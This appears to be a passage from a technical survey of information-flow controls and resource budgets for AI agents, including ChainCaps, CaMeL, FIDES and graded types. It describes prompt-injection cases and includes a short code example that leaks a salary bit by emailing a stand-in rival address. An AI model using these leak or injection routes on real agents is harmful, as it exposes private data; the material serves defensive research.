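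This can happen without an attacker, because the agent may treat the salaries as relevant to the summary. An attacker can also cause it deliberately. *A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents* (Acharya and Gupta, 2026) calls this "capability chaining" and points out that a tool for reading files and a tool for sending email are each harmless alone. Jiang and colleagues cite a testing program that found vulnerabilities involving several tools in 19 of 20 real agent applications, 365 in total.

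### Why a list of permitted tools cannot express the rule

The agent broke the rule that salaries must not leave the firm. This rule restricts the flow of data from a source to a sink, which is a point where data leaves the program or causes an effect. In two separate runs, the agent could read the salaries, fetch the industry figures, write a summary and email it to the same list. The first summary could cover only the industry figures, while the second includes the salaries. Both runs use the same tools in the same order, so a list of permitted tools must allow both or block both.

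Checking each call's arguments doesn't solve the problem either. A summary stating that the firm's engineers earn a fifth more than the industry average would reveal something about their pay without repeating any number from the spreadsheet. Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026) observe in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* that an email may be safe if its text depends only on a public document and unsafe if it depends on a sensitive file. To tell these apart, the harness needs a record of where the text came from. Their system, FORGE, records which earlier events each action may depend on, through any number of steps, and checks its rules against that record.

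### Information flow and non-interference

Information flows from an input to an output if changing the input can change the output. Non-interference is the requirement that no information flows from secret inputs to public outputs. For a program *P*, write *x* ≈ *y* if *x* and *y* have the same public parts, whatever their secret parts are. Then *P* satisfies non-interference if

*x* ≈ *y* implies *P*(*x*) ≈ *P*(*y*).

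If somebody changed every salary in the spreadsheet, the agent's outgoing emails would have to stay exactly the same.

The same definition also covers protecting actions from untrusted data if "untrusted" replaces "secret" and "trusted" replaces "public". An invoice from a stranger could not then influence a trusted action such as a payment. Researchers call this kind of protection integrity and the protection of secrets confidentiality.

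Secrets can reach an output in two ways. In an explicit flow, the program copies or transforms the secret into the output, as when the agent summarises the salaries. In an implicit flow, the secret affects what the program does. An agent that emails a recruiter only if the top salary exceeds €100,000 reveals something about that salary, even if the email is blank.

Language models complicate the definition because the same prompt can produce different answers. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) therefore require that two inputs differing only in their secrets give each public result the same probability, except for differences that arise because some runs never finish. They designed a small language for agents and proved in Lean that every program in it meets this condition, including programs that a model writes while the agent runs.

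Non-interference is often too strict for practical use. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) write in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* that enforcing it would essentially prevent an agent from making any publicly visible change after reading a secret. They instead use a weaker property called explicit secrecy. For any fixed sequence of steps, secrets must not affect the public data those steps produce, but the agent's choice of steps may still reveal something. Explicit secrecy would stop the salary summary but not the blank email to the recruiter.

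### ChainCaps: every value carries its permitted sinks

ChainCaps attaches to each value the set of sinks it may still reach. Jiang and colleagues call this set a "budget", although it contains no amounts. Each entry pairs an operation with a scope, such as sending email to addresses at a firm. A set that contains an entry also contains every narrower version of it, so permission to email anyone at the firm includes permission to email its accountant.

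Someone has to describe the data sources and tools in manifests. Each source *o* has a starting set, Init(*o*), and each tool *t* has a limit, Pass(*t*), on where its output may go. When tool *t* uses the values *x*₁, …, *xₖ* to produce *y*, the transfer rule gives *y* the set

*B*(*y*) = Pass(*t*) ∩ *B*(*x*₁) ∩ … ∩ *B*(*xₖ*).

Before a call with arguments *a* causes an effect, ChainCaps works out which sink it needs, Req(*t*, *a*), and which values contributed to its arguments, *D*(*a*). The sink rule permits the call only if

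Req(*t*, *a*) ∈ *B*(*x*) for every *x* in *D*(*a*).

In the salary case, the sets might look like this:

| | Show to the user | Email to the outside list |
|---|---|---|
| Salary spreadsheet | yes | no |
| Industry figures | yes | yes |
| Limit of the summarising tool | yes | yes |
| Summary of both | yes | no |

The agent can show the summary to the user, but ChainCaps blocks it from emailing the summary. Rewording or translating the summary would not lift the block, because no later step can add to the set.

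ChainCaps runs as a proxy between the agent and its tool servers, so it can't detect which parts of the context the model used to write an argument. It therefore keeps one set for the whole context and narrows it whenever the model reads something. Everything the model writes afterwards inherits that set. Once the agent has read the salaries, it can't even email the outside list about a change of meeting room. Resetting the set between tasks reduced these mistaken refusals from 45% to 20% in a group of difficult legitimate scenarios.

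The firm's invoice agent would run into the same difficulty. Suppose an invoice from supplier 17 may reach two sinks, a payment to supplier 17 and an email to the accountant, and the other invoices have corresponding sets of sinks. A summary of all 40 invoices could then go only to the accountant, as the firm wants. But a model that had read two suppliers' invoices in one context could no longer pay either supplier, because the two sets have only the accountant's email in common. The firm would have to handle each invoice in a separate session, and the rules still wouldn't stop a payment for a false amount.

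### Why chaining cannot add authority

Jiang and colleagues prove that a chain of calls cannot give data access to a sink that its sources lacked. Let *O*(*a*) be all the original sources that contributed to a call's arguments, directly or through other values. If ChainCaps permits the call without a special release, then

Req(*t*, *a*) ∈ Init(*o*) for every *o* in *O*(*a*).

The proof follows the data from its sources to the call:

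1. A value that comes straight from source *o* has the set Init(*o*).
2. The transfer rule gives a tool's output an intersection that includes the sets of all its inputs. If each input's set lies within the starting sets of the sources behind it, then so does the output's.
3. The sink rule requires the needed sink to be in the set of every contributing value, so it must also be in the starting set of every source.

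The mathematics is simple because an intersection never adds anything. The conclusion depends more on the assumptions that the manifests are right, the tools behave as described, and all the relevant data passes through the proxy. The theorem covers only explicit flows, so it doesn't rule out the blank email to the recruiter.

### Results on 82 tasks

Jiang and colleagues tested ChainCaps on 56 attacks and 26 legitimate tasks, running each three times with and without the proxy. An attack succeeded if restricted data reached a sink outside its set or was used to authorise one.

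| Model | Attacks that succeeded without ChainCaps | Attacks that succeeded with ChainCaps | Legitimate tasks completed with ChainCaps |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 67.8% | 4.8% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 25.2% | 3.6% | 100% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 31.5% | 3.6% | 96% |
| GPT-5.1 | 53.6% | 2.4% | 100% |
| Qwen 3.5 | 53.0% | 0.0% | 96% |

Without ChainCaps, every model completed all the legitimate tasks. The proxy added a median of 0.13 milliseconds to each call. Most of the remaining successful attacks used routes the proxy could not fully track, such as writing a script to run later or passing data between commands in a shell. The test tasks focus on this kind of failure, so the rates without ChainCaps don't measure how often ordinary agents leak data.

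These results came from carefully written manifests. In a separate test, ChainCaps blocked 100% of attacks with expert manifests and 90.9% with manifests written from a checklist. With naive manifests, it blocked only 27.3% and let the agent complete only half of the legitimate tasks. Jiang and colleagues don't give the number of attacks in this test, but the percentages would fit 11, 10 and 3 out of 11. The exact rates are uncertain, but a fall this large suggests that the protection ChainCaps gives depends on how well its manifests are written. A firm with hundreds of tools would have to state correctly, for each one, where its output may go.

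ChainCaps also did better than simplified versions of two other designs when the researchers replayed recorded attacks. On the GPT-5.1 recordings, it blocked 59.5%, while labels in the style of FIDES, a system from Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, blocked 16.1%. We can't conclude much about FIDES itself from this comparison, because the simplified version reduced each label to a single level. FIDES can also label a document with the set of people who may read it. Combining two documents then intersects their sets of readers, much as ChainCaps intersects sets of sinks.

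### CaMeL: writing the program before reading the data

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, tracks data inside a program that the agent writes. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) describes the design. One model sees the user's request but no untrusted data, and writes a Python program that makes the tool calls. A second model, which has no tools, handles tasks such as extracting a sum from an invoice. Text in the invoice can affect which of the program's branches runs, but it cannot add a call that the first model did not write.

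A custom interpreter runs the program and records where each value came from and who may read it. CaMeL calls these records "capabilities", although they are tags on data, not references that permit the use of a resource. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks a policy, which *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes as a Python function that inspects the call and its arguments, then allows or denies it. A policy could block emails containing anything derived from the salary file if the recipient may not read that file.

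The interpreter has gaps, however. Garby and colleagues point out that CaMeL raises a variable's label only on the branch that the program takes. The following program, adapted from a classic example, uses this to leak whether a salary is above €100,000:

```
skip = False
high = True
if salary > 100000: skip = True
if not skip: high = False
if high: send_email("rival@example.com", "high")
```

If the salary is above the threshold, the third line changes `skip` and marks it as secret. The fourth line does nothing, so `high` keeps its original value and public label, and the email goes out. Otherwise, `high` becomes false and no email goes out. The recipient learns one fact per run, but CaMeL retries failed programs in an ordinary Python loop that the interpreter doesn't track. Garby and colleagues argue that an attacker could use refusals in this loop to extract a whole secret bit by bit.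 TACIT avoids run-time tracking by checking the functions that work on its classified container before they run. Odersky and colleagues say that CaMeL's interpreter also accepts only a subset of Python, without user-defined functions.

### FIDES: hiding untrusted data from the planner

FIDES gives each piece of data a confidentiality label and an integrity label. Anything derived from several pieces takes the most restrictive label of each kind, so a summary of a trusted secret file and an untrusted public web page is both secret and untrusted. Costa and colleagues use two main policies. An agent may take a consequential action, such as a payment, only if the decision is based on trusted data, and it may send data only to people allowed to read all of it.

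If a model reads one untrusted email, everything it decides afterwards counts as untrusted. FIDES therefore stores untrusted results in variables and shows the model only the variables' names. To forward three emails, the model can write a call that sends the contents of a variable, which the model itself never reads. If it needs a summary, it can have a separate model without tools write one and store it in another variable. The model still sees trusted results directly, which makes planning easier than if all results were hidden.

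### AgentDojo results and later tests

Both systems performed well against the attacks in AgentDojo, but the number of tasks they completed varied widely between studies. According to *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026), CaMeL completed 77% of tasks with provable security, compared with 84% for an undefended agent.

| Test | Tasks completed without policies | Tasks completed with policies |
|---|---|---|
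| CaMeL, original result | 84% (undefended agent) | 77% |
| CaMeL, banking tasks only, rerun by Garby and colleagues | 67–71% | 37.5% |
| FIDES with GPT-4o, mean of four areas | 84% (ordinary agent) | 50% |
| FIDES's policy in FORGE, tested by Palumbo and colleagues | 79% (undefended agent) | 32% |

The CaMeL rerun covered only 16 banking tasks, so the 95% confidence interval for its score is wide, from about 11% to 64%. The score is low because several of the tasks ask the agent to read a file and act on what it says, for example by paying a bill, and CaMeL's policies don't let untrusted text determine a payment. With the policies on, no attack succeeded in any run that finished.

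In Costa and colleagues' tests, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent and none against FIDES with its policies on. AgentDojo counted three successes against FIDES, but the researchers judged these to be mistakes or actions that the policy allowed. An ordinary agent under the same policies also stopped every attack but completed only 42% of tasks. Hiding data in variables, as FIDES does, raised the completion rate by about 8 percentage points, and by 16 with the stronger model o1.

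Palumbo and colleagues tested FIDES's policy without its method of hiding data, which probably explains much of their lower figure. FIDES's policy reduced the share of attacks that succeeded from 25.2% to 1.0%. Their own policy reduced it to 0.8%, and the agent completed 57% of tasks. Their policy checks whether the user requested the action and where its target came from, instead of refusing every consequential action once the agent has read something untrusted.

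### Releasing restricted data on purpose

Useful work often requires exceptions to these rules. The firm may want to publish its average salary, or let an invoice determine a payment. Making secret data public is called declassification, and treating untrusted data as trusted is called endorsement.

In ChainCaps, an authorised person can issue a signed token that permits one call to a particular sink with data from particular sources. The firm's director could issue one to let the agent send a summary of salaries to an outside auditor. The agent couldn't use the token again or attach it to a different summary.

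FIDES can decide whether to show data to the planner based on the data's type. For example, if the agent needs to know whether an email asks for a meeting, a separate model reads the email, and the software forces it to answer yes or no. The policy may let the planner see this answer, because one bit is too small to hold a planted instruction. A free-text answer would stay hidden. A one-bit answer can still have large consequences, since a false "yes" about whether a bill is due could trigger a €9,400 payment. The AgentDojo tests did not use this type-based rule.

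Garby and colleagues' language has an explicit `endorse` operation, which makes each exception visible in the program. They prove that endorsing untrusted data can't cause secrets to leak. Their agent writes its endorsements into its program before it reads any untrusted data, so an attacker can't ask for one. With GPT-5.2, the agent completed 75% of the banking tasks. With a second model, it completed 75% with endorsement and 63% without it. With a third, it completed 65% with endorsement and 54% without it.

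Attacks succeeded in only two of 1,296 runs, both in the same scenario. The user had asked the agent to follow a file's instructions for paying a bill, and the attacker had replaced them with a different payment request. Tracking the flow from the file to the payment doesn't show whether the bill is genuine. As under Gallo's rule, an agent that made no exception would refuse both real and false bills.

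### Secure agents that are insecure together

Labels protect data only while they stay attached to it. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three agents that each ran CaMeL. A coordinator asked a database agent for information about job applicants, summarised it, and asked a notification agent to send the summary to a colleague on Slack. Someone had planted an instruction in the database to email the data to an outside address.

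The first two agents handled the planted text as untrusted data. But the coordinator then put its summary into the message containing the notification agent's instructions. That agent treated the whole message as a trusted request from its user, so it wrote a program that also sent the email. The applicants' data leaked even though each agent had followed CaMeL's rules.

The researchers fixed this by splitting each message between agents into an instruction and a set of variables. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output, and the variables keep their labels when they pass to the next agent. On a version of AgentDojo for several agents, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with a separate CaMeL for each agent, and never with the new protocol. Two older models accounted for most of the successful attacks without CaMeL, while GPT-5.5 resisted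 every attack even without it.

These tests ran without data policies, so they measured only the benefit of planning before reading. Even without those policies, giving each agent its own CaMeL reduced the share of tasks completed on an industrial maintenance benchmark by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest. The new protocol reduced it by another 3.2 points on average.

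### Spera's theorem and what it leaves open

Spera (2026), in *Safety is Non-Compositional*, proves a general result about combining systems that are safe separately. In this work, a "capability" is something a system can do, such as recognise speech or query a database, and not an unforgeable reference. "Ability" is a clearer word for it here. A rule (*S*, *T*) means that a system with all the abilities in *S* also gets those in *T*. The closure cl(*A*) contains everything that a system can reach from the abilities in *A* by applying the rules repeatedly. If *F* is the set of forbidden abilities, then *A* is safe when

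cl(*A*) ∩ *F* = ∅.

According to the theorem, two safe sets of abilities can have an unsafe union. An example with three abilities and one rule proves it. Suppose that reading salaries and sending outside email together make it possible to disclose salaries, which the firm forbids. A system with only one of those first two abilities is safe, but a system with both is not. This can't happen if every rule has a single prerequisite, because one of the parts could then reach anything the combined system could.

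Spera acknowledges that security researchers have studied such combinations for decades and that the counterexample is deliberately minimal. Spera also reports that 42.6% of about 900 recorded agent tasks included a step with several prerequisites that all had to be met. Such steps are therefore common, but the figure doesn't show whether they are dangerous.

Spera's theorem covers only checks of whether a component could reach something forbidden on its own. It doesn't support Spera's broader conclusion that checking components separately can never guarantee the safety of the whole, however carefully people design them. Peters-Gill and colleagues' protocol adds a rule about what may pass between agents, and with that rule the guarantee for each agent extends to the whole system. Checking the combined set directly is also quick, since computing a closure takes time proportional to the size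 of the rules.

Spera's theorem is compatible with the one about ChainCaps. Spera takes the union of what systems can do, which may be unsafe even if each system is safe on its own. ChainCaps takes the intersection of the destinations allowed for data. An agent with ChainCaps can still read salaries and send outside email, but having both abilities is no longer enough to disclose the salaries.

However, ChainCaps does not prevent every harmful combination. Suppose the firm allows two lists to be emailed to an outside consultant, one with employees' names and staff numbers and the other with staff numbers and salaries. If the agent joins them, the result shows what each named person earns, which neither list shows alone. ChainCaps still lets the agent email the joined list to the consultant, because both lists' permissions include that email and so their intersection does too. This is consistent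 with the theorem, since the joined list has gained no new sink.

The firm could prevent this by barring one of the lists from outside email, although that list is harmless alone. It could also write a FORGE rule blocking any outside email that depends on both lists. But if the agent sent the lists in separate sessions, each email would depend on only one list, and the consultant could combine the lists.

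## Adding amounts to permissions: how quantities combine

Most of the permissions described so far determine only whether a program may do something, such as pay supplier 17. ScopeGate also caps each payment, but a program could still make 40 payments just below the cap. A grade is an amount, attached to a type or operation, that bounds how much it uses of a resource such as euros, tool calls or bytes. A budget is the largest amount that a holder may use. If a compiler can combine the grades of a program's parts into a total, the harness can compare that total with the budget and reject an over-budget program before it makes any payments.

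The argument for doing this has three premises:

1. The harm an agent can do often depends on how much it does.
2. A yes-or-no grant limits the kind of act a program may perform, but not the amount.
3. A compiler can calculate a limit on what a whole program uses from limits on its parts.

If they hold, grants should state amounts, and compilers should check programs against them.

### Testing the premises

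When an agent handles money, the harm it can do clearly depends on the amount, and the same applies to its own running costs. *Token Budgets* (2026) catalogues 63 incidents in which agents built on language models overran their budgets. The link is weaker for secrets. A limit of 2,000 bytes on outgoing email would stop an agent from sending a whole customer database, but not a 128-bit key, which takes up only 16 bytes. An agent can also delete the only copy of a firm's accounts with a single call. Limits on amounts can therefore supplement yes-or-no permissions but can't replace them.

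Capture sets are an example of grants without amounts. A function of type `Invoice ->{bank} Unit` may use the bank connection once or a thousand times. The classifiers that Pham and colleagues added can restrict which kinds of capability a function holds, but not how much it does with them. However, a yes-or-no capability can give access to an object that enforces an amount. The firm's payer could keep a running total and refuse any payment that would take the total above €2,500.

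Some designs write the number into the grant. *AGENTCAP* (2026), which checks agents' actions as they run, gives an example of a grant for one bank transfer to a fixed recipient within 30 seconds. The grant limits the number of transfers but not the amount of money sent. *From Language Models to World-Acting Systems* (2026) recommends that agents' capabilities include limits on values, along with an expiry time and any approval they require. These limits don't require types, but putting amounts in types could let a compiler reject a program before it makes any payments. A payer that keeps a running total might refuse the thirteenth payment only after twelve have gone out.

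No algorithm can work out exactly how much every program will use, because it could then also tell which programs ever finish, which is impossible. A compiler can calculate a safe upper bound, but this may be far too high or even infinite. The compiler also needs a reliable limit for each basic operation. A payment has a limit of €200 only if the payment object rejects larger sums. The final price of a call to a language model is known only after the model has answered, so the call has a limit only if the length of the answer is capped.

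### Adding, taking the larger and multiplying

Suppose that *a* and *b* are upper bounds on what two pieces of a program use. Three rules give a bound for larger pieces:

| How the pieces run | Bound | Example with payments of up to €200 |
|---|---|---|
| one after the other | *a* ⊕ *b* = *a* + *b* | two payments: €400 |
| one or the other | *a* ⊔ *b* = max(*a*, *b*) | pay or do nothing: €200 |
| the same piece *n* times | *n* · *a* | twelve payments: €2,400 |

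The symbols come from Mannucci and Thuro (2025), in *Resource-Bounded Type Theory*, who keep them abstract so that the same rules can cover time, memory or the fees for running a program on a blockchain. Their bound for a conditional shows how the rules fit together:

bound(if *c* then *t* else *u*) = bound(*c*) ⊕ (bound(*t*) ⊔ bound(*u*)) ⊕ *δ*,

where *δ* is the fixed cost of choosing a branch. The program always evaluates the condition *c*, so its bound is added. It runs only one branch, so only the larger of the two bounds counts.

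Several quantities form a vector, and the rules apply to each component separately. A program fits its budget only if every component is within its own limit, so it can't exchange unused calls for extra euros.

Treating the components separately can make the bound too high. If one branch makes a payment, with a bound of (1 call, €200, 0 bytes), and the other sends an email, with a bound of (1 call, €0, 2,000 bytes), the combined bound is (1 call, €200, 2,000 bytes), even though no run uses both the €200 and the 2,000 bytes. A compiler could keep the alternatives separate, but a program with 20 such choices in a row could have over a million combinations.

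### The invoice program with a budget

Suppose that the firm pays its larger bills by hand, and that the agent's payment object refuses any sum over €200. The mail object refuses messages over 2,000 bytes. Leaving out the model that extracts the figures, each operation has a grade for calls, euros and bytes emailed:

| | Calls | Euros | Bytes emailed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read an invoice | 1 | 0 | 0 |
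| Pay a bill | 1 | 200 | 0 |
| Email the accountant | 1 | 0 | 2,000 |
| Budget for the program | 60 | 2,500 | 2,000 |

The agent's program reads all 40 invoices, pays at most the first twelve that are due, and sends one summary:

```
invoices = [read(f) for f in the 40 files]      # 40 · (1, 0, 0)
for inv in first 12 of due(invoices): pay(inv)  # 12 · (1, 200, 0)
email(summary(invoices))                        #  1 · (1, 0, 2000)
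```

The total is

(40, 0, 0) + (12, 2400, 0) + (1, 0, 2000) = (53, 2400, 2000),

which fits the budget of (60, 2500, 2000).

The agent might instead write a loop that reads each invoice and pays it if it is due. The bound for one invoice is then

(1, 0, 0) ⊕ ((1, 200, 0) ⊔ (0, 0, 0)) = (2, 200, 0).

Forty invoices come to (80, 8000, 0), and the email brings the total to (81, 8000, 2000), which exceeds the budget for both calls and euros. If only nine invoices are due this month, the program would make 50 calls and spend at most €1,800, but the compiler can't determine how many are due without access to the invoices. The harness can reject the program and let the agent add the cutoff of twelve, or run it with a counter that stops it when the budget runs out.

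With the cutoff, a thirteenth bill has to wait for the bookkeeper. In return, the firm knows that the program can't lose more than €2,400, whatever the invoices contain. A hidden line could still raise a bill from €94 to €200, or make an old bill look unpaid. If the genuine bills come to €1,100, false ones could take another €1,300. The budget applies equally to genuine and false bills, so the firm should set it close to what it expects to owe.

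### When the smaller limit wins

Limits combine differently from amounts used. If the firm lets agents spend up to €2,500 on any task, and the bookkeeper sets a limit of €2,000 for this one, the agent should be able to spend up to €2,000, not the sum of €4,500.

Tripathi, Kumar and colleagues (2026), in *A Policy Algebra for Trust-Preserving Agentic AI Execution*, define how an organisation's policies combine when several apply to the same agent. If two policies have budgets *B*₁ and *B*₂, the combined budget is

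min(*B*₁, *B*₂).

The agent may use only tools that both policies permit, and it needs human approval if either policy requires it. Tripathi and colleagues prove that this combined policy is the least restrictive one that satisfies both.

They also prove that combining a policy with itself changes nothing, a property called idempotence. A limit of €2,000 applied twice is still a limit of €2,000, so a harness can safely check the same policy at several levels. The sets of sinks that Jiang and colleagues attach to data are also idempotent, since intersecting a set with itself leaves it unchanged. Addition is not idempotent, since a program that spends €2,000 twice has spent €4,000.

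Confusing the two operations would be dangerous when an agent delegates work. Tripathi and colleagues require each sub-agent's budget to be no larger than that of the agent that started it. If an agent with €2,500 gives two sub-agents €2,500 each, both budgets satisfy this rule, but together the sub-agents could spend €5,000. The harness also has to divide the budget between them or track their combined spending.

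### A soundness theorem and a function called twice

Mannucci and Thuro build the addition rules into a type system. They write

Γ ⊢ᵣ;ᵦ *t* : *A*,

where the two subscripts are the budget *r* and the calculated bound *b*. The whole line means that, given the variables listed in Γ and a budget of *r*, program *t* has type *A* and uses at most *b*. Their main theorem covers programs without recursion, in which no function calls itself. It states that if *k* is what a self-contained program actually uses, then

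*k* ≤ *b* ≤ *r*.

The proof covers the typing rules one at a time. For example, in a pair of expressions, each expression uses no more than its own bound, so together they use no more than the sum of the two bounds.

However, the theorem fails for some programs that pass functions to other functions. Suppose that every function call costs 1, and that the body of a function *g* costs another 10. Now consider a function that calls its argument two times:

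twice(*f*) = (*f*(1), *f*(1)).

The rules give every variable a bound of 0, including the argument *f* inside `twice`, so the body of `twice` gets a bound of 2 for its two calls to *f*. For the program twice(*g*), the rules add this 2, 1 for calling `twice`, and the 10 for *g*, which they count only once. That makes 13. But running the program uses 1 for calling `twice` and 11 for each of the two calls to *g*, which makes 23.

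The proof goes wrong where it replaces a variable with its value and assumes that the bound stays the same. That holds for a number but not for a function, because each call to a function adds to the total. Agents' programs could easily run into this problem through `retry`, a common helper that takes a function and calls it again if it fails. If the firm's agent passed a payment function to a `retry` that made up to three attempts, the rules would count €200 instead of €600.

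To count correctly, the type of `twice` has to show that it uses its argument two times. Graded types can record this.

### Counting uses: bounded linear logic and Granule

In ordinary logic, a proof can use an assumption any number of times. Linear logic, which Jean-Yves Girard introduced in 1987, requires a proof to use each assumption exactly once unless the assumption is marked "!", which permits unlimited use. Girard and colleagues refined this in 1992 with bounded linear logic, in which !₂*A* means an *A* that a proof can use at most twice. Because proofs correspond closely to programs, language designers could turn these rules into type systems that count how often a program uses a variable.

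According to *Same Coeffect, Different Base* (Liepelt, Marshall and Orchard, 2026), two groups independently replaced the numbers with elements of any semiring in 2014. A semiring is a set of grades that a type system can add and multiply, with a 0 for "unused" and a 1 for "used once". The same rules could then track other properties, such as whether data is secret. Other researchers developed coeffect systems, which describe what a program needs from its surroundings rather than its effects on them.

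Granule is a research language that brings these ideas together. Orchard, Liepelt and Eades (2019), in *Quantitative Program Reasoning with Graded Modal Types*, show its notation with two small functions:

```
drop : t [0] → ()
copy : t [2] → (t, t)
```

The number in brackets is a grade. `drop` never uses its argument, and `copy` uses it twice. If a programmer declared that `copy` used its argument once, Granule would reject the definition.

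The rule that does most of the work for budgets is called promotion. In the notation of Liepelt and colleagues, it is:

if Γ ⊢ *t* : *A*, then *r* · Γ ⊢ [*t*] : □ᵣ *A*.

This means that if *t* has type *A* and uses the variables in Γ in the amounts listed there, then a package that allows *r* uses of *t* needs *r* times those amounts. Suppose *t* pays one bill, using the bank connection once and the supplier register twice. A package that allows 12 uses of *t* then needs 12 uses of the bank connection and 24 of the register. Every variable in Γ must have a grade, because the rule multiplies each grade by *r*. When two parts of a program share a variable, the type system adds the variable's grades from the two parts.

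Granule can use a range when a program's branches use a value different numbers of times. A function that supplies a default value when another value is missing uses the default once or not at all, so the default's grade is `0..1`. A range also sets a minimum, so a grade of `1..1` on the mail object could require the program to send exactly one summary, which an upper limit alone can't do.

Grades can also depend on other inputs. Granule's `rep` function takes a number *n* and a value, and returns a list with *n* copies of the value:

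```
rep : N n → t [n] → Vec n t
```

In Granule, a function's type can record that the function uses a value *n* times. When grades depend on such numbers, an external program checks the arithmetic. Orchard and colleagues designed Granule to demonstrate this kind of reasoning, not for general use. Grades also work in languages that are not purely functional. *Multi-graded Featherweight Java* (2023) adds them to a small model of Java.

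A limit on the number of uses caps total spending only when the amount per use is also limited. A payment object that can be used twelve times, for up to €200 each time, can spend at most €2,400. Liepelt and colleagues show that two sets of grades can be combined into pairs, with each component calculated separately, so a type system can track both the number of calls and another property.

### Putting the cost on the function type

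Mannucci and Thuro (2025), in *Resource-Bounded Martin-Löf Type Theory*, extended their system a month later in a way that also solves the problem with `twice`. A function type now carries the cost of one call:

*A* →ᵇ *B*

Every call adds *b* to the total. If the type of *g* gives an amount of 10, the two calls inside `twice` account for 11 each, and the program's total is 23, which is correct.

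The amount of a resource that code uses can depend on the size of its input. If a function uses at most *c* units per call, applying it to every item of a list of length *n* uses at most *c* · *n* + *d* units, where *d* is a fixed overhead. For a loop whose steps use different amounts, the bound is the sum of those amounts. This matters for agents because a model usually rereads the whole conversation at each turn. If every turn adds 1,000 tokens (the short pieces of text that models process), the model reads 1,000 + 2,000 + … + 20,000 = 210,000 tokens over 20 turns, not 20,000.

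These types bring back the problem that kept effect systems out of general use, because the type of `map` has to mention the cost of the function it receives. The extended system also has no rule that uses the budget to reject a program, so Mannucci and Thuro call the budget "operationally inert". A harness would itself have to compare the calculated bound with the budget. Mannucci and Thuro describe tools for the proof assistant Lean that estimate cost from the size of the code, but they do not claim that this estimate matches the bound from the types.

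### Static bounds for agent loops

Liu (2026), in *λ_A*, applies a simpler calculation to whole agents. If an agent's loop of model and tool calls has at most *n* turns and *c* is the highest cost of any call, then Liu's theorem gives

total cost ≤ *n* × *c*.

With one call per turn, as in the theorem, an agent with 20 turns and a price of $0.01 per call would cost at most $0.20. An ordinary turn has two calls, one to the model and one to a tool. Liu counts both when comparing the bound with real runs of such agents, which would make the limit $0.40 if each call cost $0.01.

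No run made more calls than its predicted bound. For two simple calculations, the bound equalled the actual number of calls. For three agents that could stop early, it was 2.5 to 3.3 times the actual number. For example, a research agent with a limit of 20 turns had a bound of 40 calls and made 15. An operator who relied on these bounds for such agents would have to set budgets at around three times normal use, or reject agents that would have stayed within a smaller budget. Five programs are too few to show how far the bound usually exceeds actual use.

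The theorem also assumes that each turn starts at most one further turn, but the types don't enforce this. If every turn started two, a limit of 20 levels would allow over a million turns. A graded type would detect this, since the program would use its reference to the rest of the loop twice instead of once.

Some agents have no limit from which to calculate a maximum cost. Liu checked 835 agent configuration files from public repositories and found 88 with no way to finish and no limit on the number of turns. The accompanying code may set a limit, but a check of the file alone would have to treat the cost as unbounded.

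### Privacy loss as a grade

Bytes are a poor measure of how much an email reveals about a person. Differential privacy provides a better one for statistics. A program *M* that adds random noise to its answers is *ε*-differentially private if, for any two sets of data *x* and *y* that differ in one person's record, and any set of answers *S*,

P(*M*(*x*) ∈ *S*) ≤ *e*^*ε* · P(*M*(*y*) ∈ *S*).

The number *ε* is the privacy loss. If it is small, the answer is almost equally likely whether or not the data include a particular person, so the answer reveals little about them. With *ε* = 0.5, including one person can make an answer at most 1.65 times as likely.

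The noise required depends on how much one person can change the true answer. A function *f* is *c*-sensitive if

|*f*(*x*) − *f*(*y*)| ≤ *c* · *d*(*x*, *y*),

where *d*(*x*, *y*) measures how far apart the inputs are, such as the number of records that differ. In 2010, Jason Reed and Benjamin Pierce designed a type system that records *c* as a grade on a function's input. Grades multiply when one function feeds another, so a 2-sensitive function followed by a 3-sensitive one is 6-sensitive. They add when a program adds the two functions' results for the same data, which gives 5. *Graded Modal Dependent Type Theory* (2020) lists this kind of sensitivity among the properties that coeffect systems can capture, along with limits on reuse and the flow of secrets.

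Suppose the firm wants to publish its total payroll and counts no more than €100,000 for any employee. Adding or removing one person changes the total by at most €100,000, so this is the sensitivity. A standard method achieves *ε* = 0.5 by adding random noise with an average size of €100,000 / 0.5 = €200,000. For 40 employees who earn €2 million in total, the published figure would typically be wrong by about 10%. For 4,000 employees who earn €200 million, the same amount of noise would be only 0.1% of the total.

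Privacy losses combine by the same rules as payments. Two answers with a loss of 0.5 each have a combined loss of at most 1, even if the same person receives both and compares them. If the program gives only one of two answers, the loss is at most the larger of the two, provided that the choice doesn't depend on the private data. If the program published a figure only when the top salary exceeded €100,000, the decision to publish would reveal whether the top salary was above that amount, and neither branch's grade includes that loss.

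A privacy budget could therefore limit what the outside consultant learns from several emails, as long as the harness keeps one running total for all sessions. But the budget would not allow the firm to send the two staff lists. An exact answer that depends on one person's record has infinite privacy loss, because no noise hides that person's effect on the answer. A summary by a language model has no known sensitivity. Privacy grades suit counts, totals and averages over many people, but most of an office agent's work is different.

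### Amounts that do not simply add

For some quantities, adding gives the wrong answer:

| Quantity | Combined amount for two steps in sequence |
|---|---|
| Calls, euros, bytes sent | the sum |
| Access level | the higher level |
| Peak memory | between the larger amount and the sum |
| Chance that at least one step goes wrong | at most the sum |
| Harm from data that someone can join | possibly more than the sum |

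*Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (2026) uses four access levels: none, read, write and admin. A skill that reads a folder and later writes to it needs write access, so combining two levels gives the higher one. This fits Mannucci and Thuro's algebra if ⊕ means "take the larger" for that component. Their own example with several quantities adds the memory each step uses. The total is safe but too high if the first step releases its memory before the second begins.

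Severity is harder to handle because somebody has to invent the scale. In a system for agents that delegate work, Muruaga (2026), in *Bounded Agents*, sets six ceilings, including limits on irreversible effects, the sensitivity of data and the cumulative "blast radius" (how much damage an agent's actions could do). Each action also gets an impact score,

*I* = *w*₁ · irreversibility + *w*₂ · blast radius + *w*₃ · sensitivity,

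where each factor lies between 0 and 1. An action whose score exceeds a threshold needs human approval.

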